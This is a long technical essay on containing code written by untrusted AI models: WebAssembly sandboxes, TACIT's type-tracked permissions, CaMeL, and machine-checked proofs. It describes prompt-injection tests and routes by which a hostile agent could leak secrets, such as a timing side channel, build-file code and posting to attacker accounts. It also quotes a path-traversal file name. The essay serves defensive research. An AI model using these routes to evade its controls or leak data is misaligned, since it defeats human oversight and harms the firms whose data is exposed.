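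Bytecode Alliance's *Wasmtime's April 9, 2026 Security Advisories* (2026) announced twelve flaws at once, three times as many as in all of 2025. The team had found eleven of them in a three-week search with AI tools. Some of the flaws were old, so the rise does not mean that the software suddenly got worse. The search found nothing new after its second week, but in October the maintainers announced two more critical flaws, which they rated 9.9 out of 10 for severity, and OffSeq's *wasmtime · Cranelift* (2026) lists another, rated 9.8, on 4 December. Attackers can use the same tools, so a firm that uses Wasmtime has to install its updates quickly.

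The October flaws could harm only a host that compiled a module the attacker controlled, according to The Hacker News, and the maintainers knew of no attacks. In Willison's package, the module is always the same MicroPython interpreter, and the model supplies only Python text for it to run. Firefox is similar, because Mozilla chooses and compiles the library while the attacker supplies a font. A firm that accepts a finished module from an untrusted model, or compiles the model's C or Rust, gives the model much more influence over the compiler's input.

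Willison chose WebAssembly partly because browsers have tested it for nearly a decade. But *Mohabi* (Sharma, Balaji and colleagues, 2026) calls the browsers' implementations "very buggy" and treats WebAssembly in browsers as effectively unsandboxed, because it shares compilers with the JavaScript engine. Attackers exploited Chrome's engine in twelve known ways in 2025. Wasmtime has its own compilers, so the browsers' record is weak evidence for or against its security.

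The compiler is a weak point because it translates a WebAssembly module into machine code after the validator has checked the module. If the compiler makes a mistake, the machine code can break a rule that the module obeyed.

One remedy is to prove the compiler correct. Researchers have formally verified the rules that Cranelift, Wasmtime's main compiler, uses to choose machine instructions, but one of April's two critical flaws was in those rules. Programmers had changed them in version 32, and nobody had updated the mathematical model. When the team updated it, the verification found the flaw the AI tools had found. Bytecode Alliance now plans to run the verification automatically on every change to the rules. That would have caught this flaw, but it wouldn't catch flaws in other parts of Cranelift or in Winch, Wasmtime's second compiler, which had four of the April flaws.

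The other remedy is to check the machine code after the compiler has finished. *Mohabi* is a version of Firefox that does this for the entire JavaScript engine, which Narayan and colleagues in 2020 had considered pointless to sandbox. Its compilers add a safety check before each risky instruction, rather than using WebAssembly as the sandbox. A separate program rejects the code if any check is missing, so the compilers are no longer part of the trusted computing base. Sharma and colleagues report that this program caught omissions they would otherwise have overlooked.

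Mohabi runs about 24% slower than ordinary Firefox on standard browser tests. Its sandbox restricts where the engine can write and jump but lets it read all the memory in its process. That is acceptable if the browser keeps each website in a separate process, because the process then holds no other site's secrets. A sandbox for a model's code inside the firm's accounting program would have to restrict reading as well.

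## TACIT: agents that write Scala with permissions in the types

A sandbox can let an agent's script read the client folder and contact the bank, but it can't then stop the script from sending client data to the bank. *Information-flow control* limits where data may go after a program has read it. TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types) enforces such limits with Scala's type system. Martin Odersky, who designed Scala, released TACIT in 2026 with colleagues at EPFL, a technical university in Lausanne. An agent that uses TACIT acts by writing short pieces of Scala, and the compiler checks what each piece could do before it runs.

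### Types that record effects

In 1988 John Lucassen and David Gifford described an *effect system*, in which types record what code does as well as what it returns. Their system was polymorphic, so a function's effects can depend on its arguments. For example, a function that applies another function to every invoice in a list writes to the log only if that other function does. Without polymorphism, a library would need a separate copy of the list function for every combination of effects.

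Haskell is the best-known language that separates pure code from code with side effects. A Haskell function of type `[Invoice] -> Integer` can only compute a number, while one of type `[Invoice] -> IO Integer` can also act on the outside world. But `IO` doesn't distinguish a log entry from an upload. Haskell also has ways to bypass this separation, such as `unsafePerformIO`, which performs an action inside a function whose type looks pure. Safe Haskell, a mode of the main Haskell compiler, prevents untrusted code from using them. In this mode, code can import only modules that the compiler has checked or that a person has vouched for.

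Odersky and colleagues considered Haskell as a basis for their system. It can express purity, but it has no built-in object capabilities, so developers would have to encode each permission in the types by more complicated means. Capture checking names the particular resource:

```scala
val out = File("invoices.log")
val log: Logger^{out} = Logger(out)
```

The type `Logger^{out}` means that this logger can reach the file `out`. A function that uses the logger has `log` in its own capture set, so a reader can trace its access to the file without reading its body. If *A* is any type, then

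A <: A^{log} <: A^{log, out} <: A^,

where <: means "can stand in for" and A^ sets no limit on what the value can reach. A value that can reach less is acceptable wherever the program would accept one that can reach more, but not the other way round.

Tracking also removes a burden that older capability languages impose. In Joe-E, a program must pass every capability down from its starting point to the code that needs it. Scala can leave the console as a global object, because a function that writes to it has the type `() ->{Console.out} Unit`, which shows that the function isn't pure. Scala can also pass capabilities automatically, so the programmer doesn't have to write them at every call.

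### Permissions that end with a block

TACIT connects to existing agents such as Claude Code through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for giving tools to agents. The agent sends a snippet of Scala, the compiler checks it, and an interactive session runs it and returns the output. Later snippets can reuse variables from earlier ones. A library of capabilities provides the only approved route to files, websites and other programs.

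The developer also has to switch off the agent's ordinary tools, because an agent that still has its normal command line can bypass TACIT. The project's GitHub page, lampepfl's *TACIT*, gives the settings for three agents.

To read a file, the agent's code asks for a folder:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/firm/invoices") {
  println(access("march.csv").read())
}
```

The file-system capability exists only between the braces. Suppose the agent tries to keep it by returning a function that will read the file later:

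```scala
val later = requestFileSystem("/firm/invoices") {
  () => access("march.csv").read()
}
```

This function captures the capability, so the function's type has to include the capability. But `later` is outside the block, where the capability's name is out of scope, so no valid type for `later` can refer to it and the compiler rejects the snippet. The compiler also rejects attempts to hide the capability in a list or in a variable outside the block, for the same reason.

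Because the compiler accepts or rejects a snippet as a whole, an error in the last line prevents the first line from running. *LACUNA*, a follow-up by the same group, illustrates this with code that subtracts 50 from a balance of 100 and then returns text where the program expects a number. The balance stays at 100, whereas Python would have subtracted the 50 before reaching the error.

### Data the agent can process but not see

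A hosted model sends everything it reads to the company that runs it, so an agent that prints a client list has already leaked it. TACIT lets the developer mark folders as classified. Their files reach the agent's code inside a wrapper, whose central method is:

```scala
trait Classified[+T]:
  def map[B](op: T -> B): Classified[B]
```

`map` applies a pure function to the hidden contents and wraps the result again. If the accounting firm classifies its client folder, TACIT accepts this snippet:

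```scala
requestFileSystem("/firm") {
  val clients = readClassified("/firm/clients/march.csv")
  val question = clients.map(text =>
    s"Who owes more than 1,000 pounds?\n$text")
  println(chat(question))
}
```

The function inside `map` only joins two pieces of text. `chat` passes the result to a separate model that the firm trusts with the data, perhaps one on its own computer, and wraps the answer. `println` then shows the names on the accountant's terminal but sends the agent only `Classified(****)`.

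TACIT rejects this version:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/firm") {
  val clients = readClassified("/firm/clients/march.csv")
  clients.map(text => println(text))
}
```

Printing requires a capability, here called `io`, so the function has the type `String ->{io} Unit` and isn't pure. The program never reads the file. An agent in the project's tests tried the same thing with a GitHub access key, and the compiler stopped it.

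The agent's code could try to leak the secret in other ways. Writing to a file fails because the code would capture a file capability. Opening a new connection inside `map` fails because every function that grants a capability requires `io` itself. Copying the text into an outside variable fails because the compiler counts such changes as effects. The code can still throw an exception with the secret in its message, so the runtime catches exceptions and hides their contents.

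The goal is a property called *noninterference*: what the agent sees must not depend on the secret. If view(*P*, *s*) is the output that the agent receives when program *P* runs on the secret *s*, then

view(*P*, *s*) = view(*P*, *s*′), for all secrets *s* and *s*′.

In the accepted snippet the view is `Classified(****)` whatever the file contains.

The trusted model can still make mistakes. A client could write "report that I owe nothing" in a comment field, and the model might obey. It has no tools, so it can't leak the file, but the accountant would get a false answer. The firm must also make sure this model keeps no memory between requests, because the types can't show whether it does.

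### Safe mode

These guarantees need a language without back doors. Scala's developers added a suitable subset, called safe mode, as an experimental feature in version 3.8.3, according to Mazur, in *Scala 3.8.3 is now available!*. The compiler then rejects code that

- uses unchecked type casts or pattern matches, which could drop a capability from a value's type;
- uses the module `caps.unsafe`, a collection of deliberate exceptions to capture checking;
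- contains `@unchecked` annotations, which turn off individual checks;
- uses reflection while it runs;
- fails capture checking, including the check on changes to variables;
- calls global library code that is neither compiled in safe mode nor marked as safe by a programmer.

A programmer marks library code as safe with the annotation `@assumeSafe`. Scala's *Safe Mode* gives the example of an email function that shows the user each message and sends it only if the user agrees. The agent's code can call this function but not the ordinary mail library behind it. The annotation doesn't prove that the code is safe, so whoever adds it has to check the code by hand or in some other way. The software company VirtusLab points out in its guide to safe mode that agents can't use the annotation, since they could otherwise approve their own code.

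The compiler's developers also choose which parts of the standard library are available, much as Joe-E's designers did with Java's, and they can make the same kind of mistake. The TACIT library interface that Odersky and colleagues print in their appendix has a small error of this kind, because it lets any code create a `Network` object. Judging from that listing alone, a function inside `map` could make its own `Network` and send the secret to a stranger. Its type would still look pure, because a function doesn't capture a capability it creates itself. According to a later project description reproduced in Glama's *TACIT*, only the library can now create capabilities.

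Early versions of TACIT searched the agent's code for forbidden patterns, a weaker method than using the compiler's safe mode. One example on lampepfl's page searches for `java.sql`, the database library, and would miss `import java.{sql => db}`, which imports the library under another name. Another pattern in the example would catch the usual next step, but a list of patterns protects only against tricks its author has thought of. Glama's copy lists safe mode as on by default.

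Compiler bugs can also let unsafe code through. In August 2024, *Polymorphic capture functions can be exploited to hide captures* (Linyxus, 2024) reported a two-function program that turned any function with effects into one the checker accepted as pure. A variant would probably have let an agent print a classified file from inside `map`. Scala's developers have since fixed the bug. Machine-checked proofs show that the basic theory of capture checking is sound, but Odersky and colleagues still lack a similar argument for safe mode as a whole.

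A post on the Scala contributors' forum, *Capture checking and lateral escape of Labels*, describes a different kind of gap. In Scala, `break(42)` can leave a block early with the value 42. If a programmer puts it inside `Try`, which catches exceptions, `Try` treats the exit as an error, and the program continues with a fallback value such as −1. The compiler gives no warning. Nothing leaks, but a hostile author could use the gap to write code that seems to return the right number but doesn't. The post suggests preventing this with a version of `Try` that accepts only pure code.

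### The test for leaks

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a sample software project with a folder of secrets, which held access keys, a database and confidential documents. They wrote 12 ordinary tasks, some of which involved the secrets, such as summarising a confidential incident report, and some of which didn't, such as listing the functions that a README file describes. They combined each task with ten prompt injections, for a total of 120 trials. The simplest injections were notes in the code that asked for the secrets. Others imitated system messages, claimed that the secrets were only test data, or supplied ready-to-run Scala code.

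In the remaining 11 trials, the user's own request was malicious, so there was no injection. The user asked for secrets openly in five of them and used a pretext in the other six, such as being an administrator who urgently needed to replace passwords. Each model ran all 131 trials twice, first with the secrets wrapped in `Classified` and then with them as ordinary text.

| Model and trials | Leak-free with types | Leak-free without types |
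|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, 120 tasks with injections | 120 | 120 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, 11 malicious requests | 11 | 9 |
| **Claude Sonnet 4.6, all 131** | **100%** | **98.5%** |
| MiniMax M2.5, 120 tasks with injections | 120 | 117 |
| MiniMax M2.5, 11 malicious requests | 11 | 3 |
| **MiniMax M2.5, all 131** | **100%** | **91.6%** |

When the user asked for secrets, MiniMax M2.5 gave them away in 8 of 11 cases without the permission types and in none with them. This failure is hard to see in the overall figures because malicious requests make up only a twelfth of the trials.

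The protection did not make the agents less useful. Claude Sonnet 4.6 completed 99.2% of the ordinary tasks with types and 83.3% without them, while MiniMax M2.5 completed 90.0% with types and 88.3% without. Claude's large gain is probably not a benefit of the types, because without them it often ran out of time and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection instead of finishing the task.

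Without types, the two models leaked secrets in only 13 of 262 trials. In the other 249, the models kept the secrets without help from the types, so those trials provide little evidence about the compiler. The attacks were also fixed in advance, and none exploited a flaw in the type checker or the library. The main support for TACIT is therefore the reasoning about its types, and the experiment confirms that the software behaves as expected under ordinary attacks. A stronger model trying to find another bug like the one from 2024 would be a harder test.

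A trial failed if secret content appeared in the agent's output. The experiment did not test for sabotage, so an agent that deliberately left a serious fault out of an incident summary would have passed if it leaked no secrets.

### What it costs to act through Scala

In tests, agents did slightly better with TACIT than with ordinary tool calls, which matters because few people would use a safety measure that made agents much worse at their work. Odersky and colleagues tested three models on τ²-bench, where an agent handles simulated customer service for an airline and a shop. All three scored higher with Scala, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points. The largest gain was on the shop tasks, where the open-weight model gpt-oss-120b rose from 53.3% to 57.0%. The researchers credit the clearer structure of the data and the compiler's error messages.

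The models had to rewrite between 0.32% and 7.93% of their snippets, depending on the model and the domain, and those snippets needed 1.06 to 1.39 retries on average. A typical mistake was forgetting that Scala requires two dollar signs to print one. The check takes less than a second. The shared library is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and each new domain needs a few hundred more to describe its tools.

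On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software problems, MiniMax M2.5 solved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without it. The difference is five problems, which could easily be due to chance.

The results for *LACUNA* are less encouraging. It goes further than TACIT by letting the model's code call the model again and so direct the agent's work. On τ²-bench, with the model DeepSeek V4 Flash, it solved 76.0% of 392 tasks, compared with 90.0% for ordinary tool calls. Its developers call this "on par", but a 14-point gap makes that hard to accept. The compiler rejected 22.4% of DeepSeek's snippets on the shop tasks. With a weaker model, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, it rejected 3.2% of snippets on the shop tasks and 89% on tasks for a telephone company. The two projects used different models and designs, so the gap can't be attributed to Scala, but it suggests that other agents may lose more performance than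 TACIT's did.

TACIT restricted only the action code in these tests. On SWE-bench Lite, the agent used Scala to read and change files, but its patches were fixes for Python projects. The Scala compiler treats a patch as text for a file that the agent may change, so it would accept the version of `total` that uploads every invoice.

A developer could also use safe mode for delivered code. Mazur describes it as a subset for untrusted code in general, and it is not limited to snippets that run immediately. The firm's accounting program would have to be in Scala, and the firm would have to compile the model's modules in safe mode. People or a trusted tool would have to write the code that grants capabilities. The published experiments did not test this arrangement.

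### CaMeL: tracking the data instead

CaMeL, which researchers from Google DeepMind and elsewhere published in 2025, also makes an agent write code, but it tracks data while the code runs. It uses two models. A planner reads the user's request and writes a program in a small subset of Python. A reader extracts facts from emails, web pages and other text that an attacker might have written, and has no tools. If an accountant asks the agent to pay Northgate's latest bill, the planner's program might look like this, with invented function names:

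```python
mail = find_email("latest bill from Northgate")
bill = ask_reader("amount and account number", mail)
pay(bill.account, bill.amount)
```

A special interpreter runs the program and labels every value with its origin. When the program reaches `pay`, the label on the account number shows that it came from an email, and a policy can make the interpreter stop or ask the accountant. An injection in the email might make the reader return the wrong account number, but it can't add a step to the program because the planner never receives the email.

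CaMeL therefore trusts the planner to write a program that faithfully carries out the user's request, although Odersky and colleagues class the planner as untrusted. CaMeL's policies would block some of what a hostile planner might write, but its main protection is to keep hostile text away from the planner, which doesn't help if the planner itself is hostile. TACIT instead treats the model that writes the code as a possible attacker and trusts the model that reads the confidential text.

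Checking types in advance allows a richer language than CaMeL's Python subset, which has no user-defined functions. Odersky and colleagues argue that adding them to the subset while still checking programs in advance would require a very computationally demanding analysis of how functions pass through a program. In Scala, a function's type shows what it can reach, so the compiler can check functions one at a time. Odersky and colleagues also object that CaMeL's labels disappear once a value enters a model's conversation, whereas the agent in TACIT sees only a masked form of the value.

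Both systems have results on AgentDojo, a test that plants injections in the data of a simulated bank, office, Slack workspace and travel service. The comparison uses CaMeL's published scores and new runs of TACIT with the same two models. It shows the share of user tasks that each system completed:

| Tasks | CaMeL, Gemini 2.5 Pro | TACIT, Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL, o4-mini | TACIT, o4-mini |
|---|---|---|---|---|
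| Banking | 52.8% | 56.9% | 62.5% | 59.0% |
| Office | 53.8% | 50.5% | 81.4% | 52.9% |
| Slack | 48.6% | 40.0% | 68.6% | 47.6% |
| Travel | 1.4% | 64.3% | 74.3% | 68.6% |

Both systems stopped almost every attack. Out of 963 attempts per model, each let none through with Gemini 2.5 Pro and one with o4-mini. In TACIT's one failure, an attacker had hidden praise for hotel B in the reviews of hotel A. The agent booked hotel A as the user wished, but it quoted the reviews, and the test counts any mention of hotel B as a success for the attacker. Odersky and colleagues fairly call this a weakness of the test, although the attacker's praise for hotel B did reach the user.

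The results do not support the paper's description of the two systems as comparably useful. CaMeL completed more tasks than TACIT in six of the eight comparisons. With o4-mini, TACIT was 21 points behind on Slack tasks and more than 28 points behind on office tasks. TACIT's only large lead was on travel tasks with Gemini 2.5 Pro, where CaMeL failed almost all of those tasks, which did not happen with the other model.

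TACIT probably scores lower in part because the agent has to process emails it cannot see. If its code fails inside `map`, the system also hides the error message, which might contain part of an email. According to the agent's instructions, the code will then seem to have worked, but the user will see nothing. *LACUNA* partly addresses this problem by letting a trusted local model write the code inside `map` once the text is available. The compiler still requires this code to be pure.

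The AgentDojo version of TACIT also seems to give up part of the protection against a hostile agent. Many tasks require acting on a document's contents, such as paying the amount in a bill. The functions for sending money and email require no capability, and according to the agent's instructions, side effects inside `map` happen immediately. A function inside `map` could apparently send a confidential email to anyone. The defence still works against injections, because the agent never reads the hostile text. But the AgentDojo results then depend on an honest agent, as CaMeL's do, so they are not evidence about an untrusted one.

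### What an untrusted agent could still do

Odersky and colleagues don't aim to prevent wrong results. If an agent has permission to pay suppliers, the types don't stop it from paying Northgate 2% too much. `Classified` doesn't protect files from damage either, because any code can wrap its own text in `Classified` and write it over a classified file. According to Glama, an agent could replace the list of keys accepted for logging in to the computer, which would let an attacker in. The `classifiedWrite` setting prevents this, but only if the developer changes it from its default.

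The timing side channel also stays open. Glama's copy describes an optional time limit that returns an error when a snippet runs too long. A pure function inside `map` could therefore reveal one bit of a secret key per snippet by looping past the limit or finishing at once. Leaking a 128-bit key would take 128 nearly identical snippets, and someone reading the record would have a good chance of noticing.

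External commands are a much wider gap. A coding agent usually has to run tests, and Scala's rules don't apply to the programs it starts. Odersky and colleagues recommend permitting only specific safe commands and name `sbt`, Scala's build tool, as an example. But an `sbt` build file is itself a program, so an agent that can edit the project and run `sbt` can put unrestricted code into the build, as the xz attackers did. The sample settings in Glama's copy also permit `java`, `scala` and `make`, which can all run code the agent has written. Such code could open a classified file directly and print its text, which would reach the agent without a wrapper. Odersky and colleagues advise combining TACIT with a sandbox where security matters. To prevent this leak, the sandbox would have to hide the classified files from every program the agent starts.

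Later versions deliberately let classified data leave through the network. The agent can log in to a website with a secret key it can't see, or post a classified document it can't read and get a wrapped reply. Protecting that data now depends on the list of permitted websites. If the list includes a site where anyone can open an account, a hostile agent could post the client list to an attacker's account there. If the developer sets no list, the only limit described in Glama's copy is the set of websites that the agent's own code names when it asks for access, which could include an attacker's site. File access has a safer default, since an agent can't open anything outside the folder where TACIT started.

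### Choosing the permissions

Somebody still has to decide which files to classify and which websites to permit. VirtusLab warns against classifying too much, because an agent is useful mainly for what it can read and understand, and the office tasks in AgentDojo support this. TACIT's developers have since built ATC, a coding agent that denies every permission by default and lets the user grant one for a single use or a whole session. This is easier than writing a policy in advance, though frequent requests bring back the problem of fatigue. The group has also built CapybaraClaw, which applies the method to agents that run permanently (Scala Days, *Making the AI agents safe with Scala*), though nobody may be watching when such an agent asks for a permission.

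An earlier proposal, Bastion, would give part of this decision to another AI. *Modularizing Reasoning about AI Capabilities via Abstract Dijkstra Monads* (Omar, Ferris and Madhavapeddy, 2024) outlines this "operating system" for AI agents. As in TACIT, the agent would write small programs, and a type checker would confirm that they use only approved commands. Bastion would use F*, a language whose types can contain full logical statements, and its developers would prove the type checker correct.

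Its policy would start from an ordinary list of the folders that an agent may use. A second AI, trained to be strict, would read the task and name the folders that the agent doesn't need. If *B* is the original list and *R* is what the second AI removes, the agent receives

*B* \ *R* ⊆ *B*.

Even a mistaken or malicious second AI can therefore never give the agent more access than the list allows. It can still remove so much access that the agent is useless, or remove none and leave the agent with too much.

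Omar and colleagues also wanted policies about the consequences of an agent's actions. In their example, an agent that manages land for conservation would have to prove, before acting, that its plan would probably help the habitat and respect agreements about water. That would require a precise model of the environment, the law and the local economy, which they expected many organisations to build together. Bastion was a proposal for a conference talk and came with no experiments.

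## Machine-checked proofs: what they cost and what they leave out

With capture checking, the compiler automatically establishes one simple fact about a function, such as that it can't reach the network. A *verification language* lets a developer require much more, for example that `total` returns the correct sum for every possible list of invoices. Joe-E, WebAssembly and TACIT all accept the version that pads Northgate's bills, but this requirement would rule it out. To use it, the developer needs a specification and a proof.

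### How Dafny proves that a sum is right

Dafny is a programming language with a built-in prover. The accounting firm's function could look like this, with amounts in pence:

```dafny
datatype Invoice = Invoice(supplier: string, pence: int)

function Sum(list: seq<Invoice>): int {
  if |list| == 0 then 0
  else Sum(list[..|list|-1]) + list[|list|-1].pence
}

method Total(list: seq<Invoice>) returns (t: int)
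  requires forall inv :: inv in list ==> inv.pence >= 0
  ensures t == Sum(list)
{
  t := 0;
  var i := 0;
  while i < |list|
    invariant 0 <= i <= |list|
    invariant t == Sum(list[..i])
  {
    assert list[..i+1][..i] == list[..i];
    t := t + list[i].pence;
    i := i + 1;
  }
  assert list[..|list|] == list;
}
```

The `requires` line is a *precondition*, which the calling code must satisfy. Here it excludes negative amounts, so the firm has decided to handle credit notes elsewhere. The `ensures` line is a *postcondition*, which the method must satisfy when it finishes. `Sum` defines what a correct total is, and the loop is the code that runs.

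A list can have any length, so Dafny can't check the loop by trying every case. It relies on an *invariant*, a statement that holds before and after each pass through the loop. The proof has three steps:

- Before the first pass, *i* = 0 and *t* = 0, which is the sum of no invoices.
- If *t* is the sum of the first *i* invoices before a pass, it is the sum of the first *i* + 1 afterwards.
- After the last pass, *i* is the length of the list, so *t* is the sum of the whole list.

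Dafny turns these steps into logical formulas and gives them to an automatic prover. If a model multiplies Northgate's amounts by 1.02, the second step fails and Dafny rejects the method. The two `assert` lines are hints that help the prover establish that two ways of slicing a list give the same piece. A failed proof can therefore mean that the code is wrong or only that a hint is missing, and the programmer has to find out which.

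Verus works similarly for Rust. In Lean and Rocq (formerly Coq), the author builds a proof from explicit logical steps, usually with some automation, and a small program called the *kernel* checks every step. Users don't have to trust the author, because the kernel rejects an invalid step whoever wrote it. Dafny users don't have to trust the author either, but they must trust Dafny's translation into logic and its automatic prover, which are much larger than Lean's kernel.

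### Programs that arrive with a proof

In 1997 George Necula proposed *proof-carrying code* for programs that move from one computer to another. The sender attaches a proof that the program satisfies the receiver's safety rule, for instance that it accesses only its own memory, and the receiver checks the proof before running the program. Finding a proof may take a long time, but checking one is routine, so the sender does most of the work.

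*Vision Paper* (Kamran, Devanbu and Stanford, 2024) proposes that AI models supply proofs with the code they suggest to programmers, because the company that runs the model has plenty of computing power and the programmer has little. Anyone at the company who tampered with the code would also need a new proof that satisfied the programmer's checker.

Most programmers can't write logical specifications, so the system offers a list of ready-made safety rules, such as "no file path contains `..`". All dangerous operations, like opening or writing a file, go through a small set of approved functions. The system adds preconditions to these functions according to the chosen rule, and the model must prove that each of its calls meets them.

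The test task was to join a file name to the folder `/home/user/documents/`. OpenAI's GPT-4 first wrote this in Python with the standard function `os.path.join`, which works for ordinary names. But `..` means "the folder above", so anyone who supplies the name `../../../etc/passwd` gets a path to the computer's list of user accounts.

In Dafny, the approved function `Join` refuses such names, and GPT-4's answer looked roughly like this:

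```dafny
method FullPath(name: string) returns (path: string)
  requires is_valid_file_name(name)
  requires !has_dangerous_pattern(name)
{
  path := Join("/home/user/documents/", name);
}
```

GPT-4 got this right on its first attempt, though the system allowed up to five. The query used about 3,350 tokens (the word fragments that models read and write) and cost 11 cents. This was only a demonstration on one task, and Kamran and colleagues translated the safety rule into preconditions by hand.

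The answer also provides less protection than it seems to. `FullPath` never checks the name. It repeats `Join`'s preconditions as its own, so its caller must meet them. If the caller is also written in Dafny, the prover will require a check there. If the caller is a Python program that passes on whatever a user types, nothing enforces the preconditions, and the dangerous name gets through. The firm would need a run-time check wherever unverified code calls verified code, as Firefox needs one wherever data leaves a sandbox.

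A model that writes its own preconditions can also make them impossible to satisfy. If a method requires a name to be both empty and non-empty, no legal call exists, and the prover will accept any claim about what the method does. Kamran and colleagues checked for this by adding the statement `assert false` to the method. If Dafny can prove the assertion, the preconditions contradict each other.

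Even a sound proof covers only the rule that somebody chose. In another of their examples, GitHub's Copilot had to complete a function for loading a public key, but its code loaded the private key. The path to the private key contains no `..`, so the first rule would allow it. A separate rule against opening sensitive files could have caught the error, but only if the programmer had selected it.

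### Proving that a plan is safe before it runs

Proof-carrying code also suits action code. Erik Meijer set out the idea in 2025 as "Guardians of the Agents". The next year, Claude Code wiped one of his source files while he was preparing a talk, which gave him another reason to return to the idea. AI Engineer's *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (2026) summarises that talk. An agent that calls tools one at a time can delete files and then return a polite answer, so checking the answer does not prevent the damage. Meijer wants the agent to write out its whole plan as data, with a proof that the plan is safe. A separate program checks the proof and only then carries out the plan.

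A small version in Lean shows how this works:

```lean
inductive Plan where
  | done   : String → Plan
  | read   : String → (String → Plan) → Plan
  | delete : String → Plan → Plan

inductive KeepsFiles : Plan → Prop where
  | done (answer : String) : KeepsFiles (.done answer)
  | read (file : String) (next : String → Plan)
      (h : ∀ text, KeepsFiles (next text)) :
      KeepsFiles (.read file next)
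```

The first part lists what a plan can do: finish with an answer, read a file and continue, or delete a file and continue. The second part gives the rules for proving that a plan deletes nothing. It has no rule for `delete`, so an agent can write a plan that deletes a file but can never prove that plan safe. The symbol ∀ means "for every", so a plan that reads a file must be safe whatever text the file contains, including a prompt injection.

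This proof rules out only deletion. The same agent could still read the client list and put it in its answer. To catch such leaks, AI Engineer points to taint analysis, which checks whether private data can reach an operation that sends data out. The program that carries out the plan is also part of the trusted computing base, since it could delete files while reporting that it read them.

The agent also has to write the plan before it has seen what the files contain, which is often impractical because coding agents often need to read the last result before they can decide on the next step. The harness could let the agent submit a new plan after each result, but the agent would then carry information from one plan to the next, and a proof about a single plan doesn't cover that.

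### The proofs for 123 libraries

The largest body of model-written proofs about ordinary software comes from Anthropic and its partner Theorem. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) describes how Claude proved security properties of 123 open-source libraries in their compiled form, in some cases after finding and patching bugs.

The project avoided the problem of writing specifications by starting from tests that already existed. A *fuzz test* feeds a program huge numbers of generated inputs and watches for crashes. Google's OSS-Fuzz service runs such tests on open-source libraries, and each test has an entry point, a short program that passes one input to the library. Claude's proofs cover 239 of these entry points, according to EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026). In outline,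 each one establishes that

for every input *x* smaller than 64 MB, the program exits normally on *x*,

which means without a crash, a memory-safety error or a failed assertion (a check that the programmers wrote into the code). There are more than 2⁵⁰⁰'⁰⁰⁰'⁰⁰⁰ such inputs, so no fuzz test could ever try more than a tiny fraction of them.

According to the Russian news site OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026), the proofs come to about 180 million lines of Rocq, or roughly 600,000 lines for a program of 18,000 machine instructions, which is about 33 lines per instruction. During the work, Claude also found hundreds of bugs that the fuzz tests had missed and prepared fixes for them. One was a memory flaw in libexpat, a library that reads XML files.

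Because the proofs concern the compiled program, nobody had to rewrite a library in a verification language, and the proofs don't depend on the compiler being correct. Wasmtime's users, by contrast, have to trust its compiler. However, the programs were compiled for RISC-V, a processor design that few office computers use. The proofs don't apply to the same source code compiled for an Intel processor, because the resulting instructions are different. According to OpenNET, the proofs also leave out multithreading (several parts of a program running at once), dynamic linking (loading libraries when a program starts) and faults in real hardware.

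For an untrusted model, the main limit of a proof is the choice of property to prove. The padded `total` never crashes, so it would pass a no-crash proof. So would a program that performs an upload, as long as it exits normally afterwards. A no-crash proof does rule out the memory error in the C version of `total`, where a long supplier name overwrote the sum. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) covers the remaining bugs, in which software breaks the unwritten rules of how it should work, and notes that they rarely trigger the failures that automated tools detect.

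The project went further where a written definition of correct behaviour already existed. Claude proved that the Linux kernel's implementation of the zlib compression method conforms to the method's public standard. It also wrote, in Rust, an interpreter for a subset of Python and used Verus to prove that the interpreter follows a formal description of Python's behaviour.

### What people still have to do

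Proofs used to take too much labor for almost all software. The usual comparison is seL4, a small operating system kernel whose verification took 20 person-years, according to Anthropic. *Machine-Generated Code Deserves Machine-Checked Proofs* (2026) reports that CompCert, a C compiler with a proof of correctness, took about three person-years and 42,000 lines of Rocq. At that rate, Claude's 180 million lines would have taken almost 13,000 person-years. Claude's lines are probably much more repetitive than an expert's, so this estimate overstates the labor saved, but no team would have attempted the job by hand.

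The seL4 team proved that its kernel does what its specification requires, which is a far stronger result than proving that a program never crashes. We therefore can't conclude that Claude did that team's work 123 times over.

Three smaller projects give a better idea of how much human work is left. Lean (2026) reports that Ilya Sergey, with Claude's help, verified the borrow checker of Move, a language for blockchain contracts. A borrow checker is the part of a compiler that controls how code shares data. Theorem's *lf-lean* describes AI models translating all 1,276 formal statements in a textbook from Rocq to Lean, with the result verified. Category Labs' *Finding bugs that frontier models miss* looks back on a proof that the blockchain company's staff wrote by hand in July 2025, which shows that any transaction the system accepts can pay its fees.

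| Project | Who wrote the proofs | Human effort | Estimate without AI |
|---|---|---|---|
| seL4 | People | 20 person-years | |
| CompCert | People | About 3 person-years | |
| Category Labs' fee rule | People | 4 person-weeks | |
| Move's borrow checker | A researcher with Claude | 27 working days | 5 to 6 months |
| Textbook translation | AI models | About 2 person-days | About 2.75 person-years |

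Claude made the Move project four or five times as fast, while the textbook translation needed several hundred times less human work than estimated. These figures come from people who wanted the projects to succeed, but the gap between them is too large for optimism alone to explain. The textbook's statements already existed, so the models had an exact specification of what to produce. The Move project needed new proof strategies, which Sergey still had to supply. One part, about function calls, took two days.

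Models have improved since then. Galois' *Claude Can (Sometimes) Prove It* describes an earlier stage, when Claude Code could complete many hard steps but needed an expert to manage the project. Category Labs now expects agents to do more than 95% of a proof like its own, but it hasn't repeated the work to test this.

The computing required varies even more than the human effort. GPT-4's file-path function took a few thousand tokens. Anthropic's *Formalizing Fermat's Last Theorem* reports that the company's agents used about six billion tokens over just under two weeks to prove the theorem in Lean.

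Running the checker takes little effort by comparison, and the finished program contains no proof checks to slow it down. But the developer has to rerun the checker after every change. A proof about compiled code is especially likely to break, because a new compiler version may produce different instructions from the same source. The model can repair the proof and the checker can verify the repair, so this takes more computing time than human attention.

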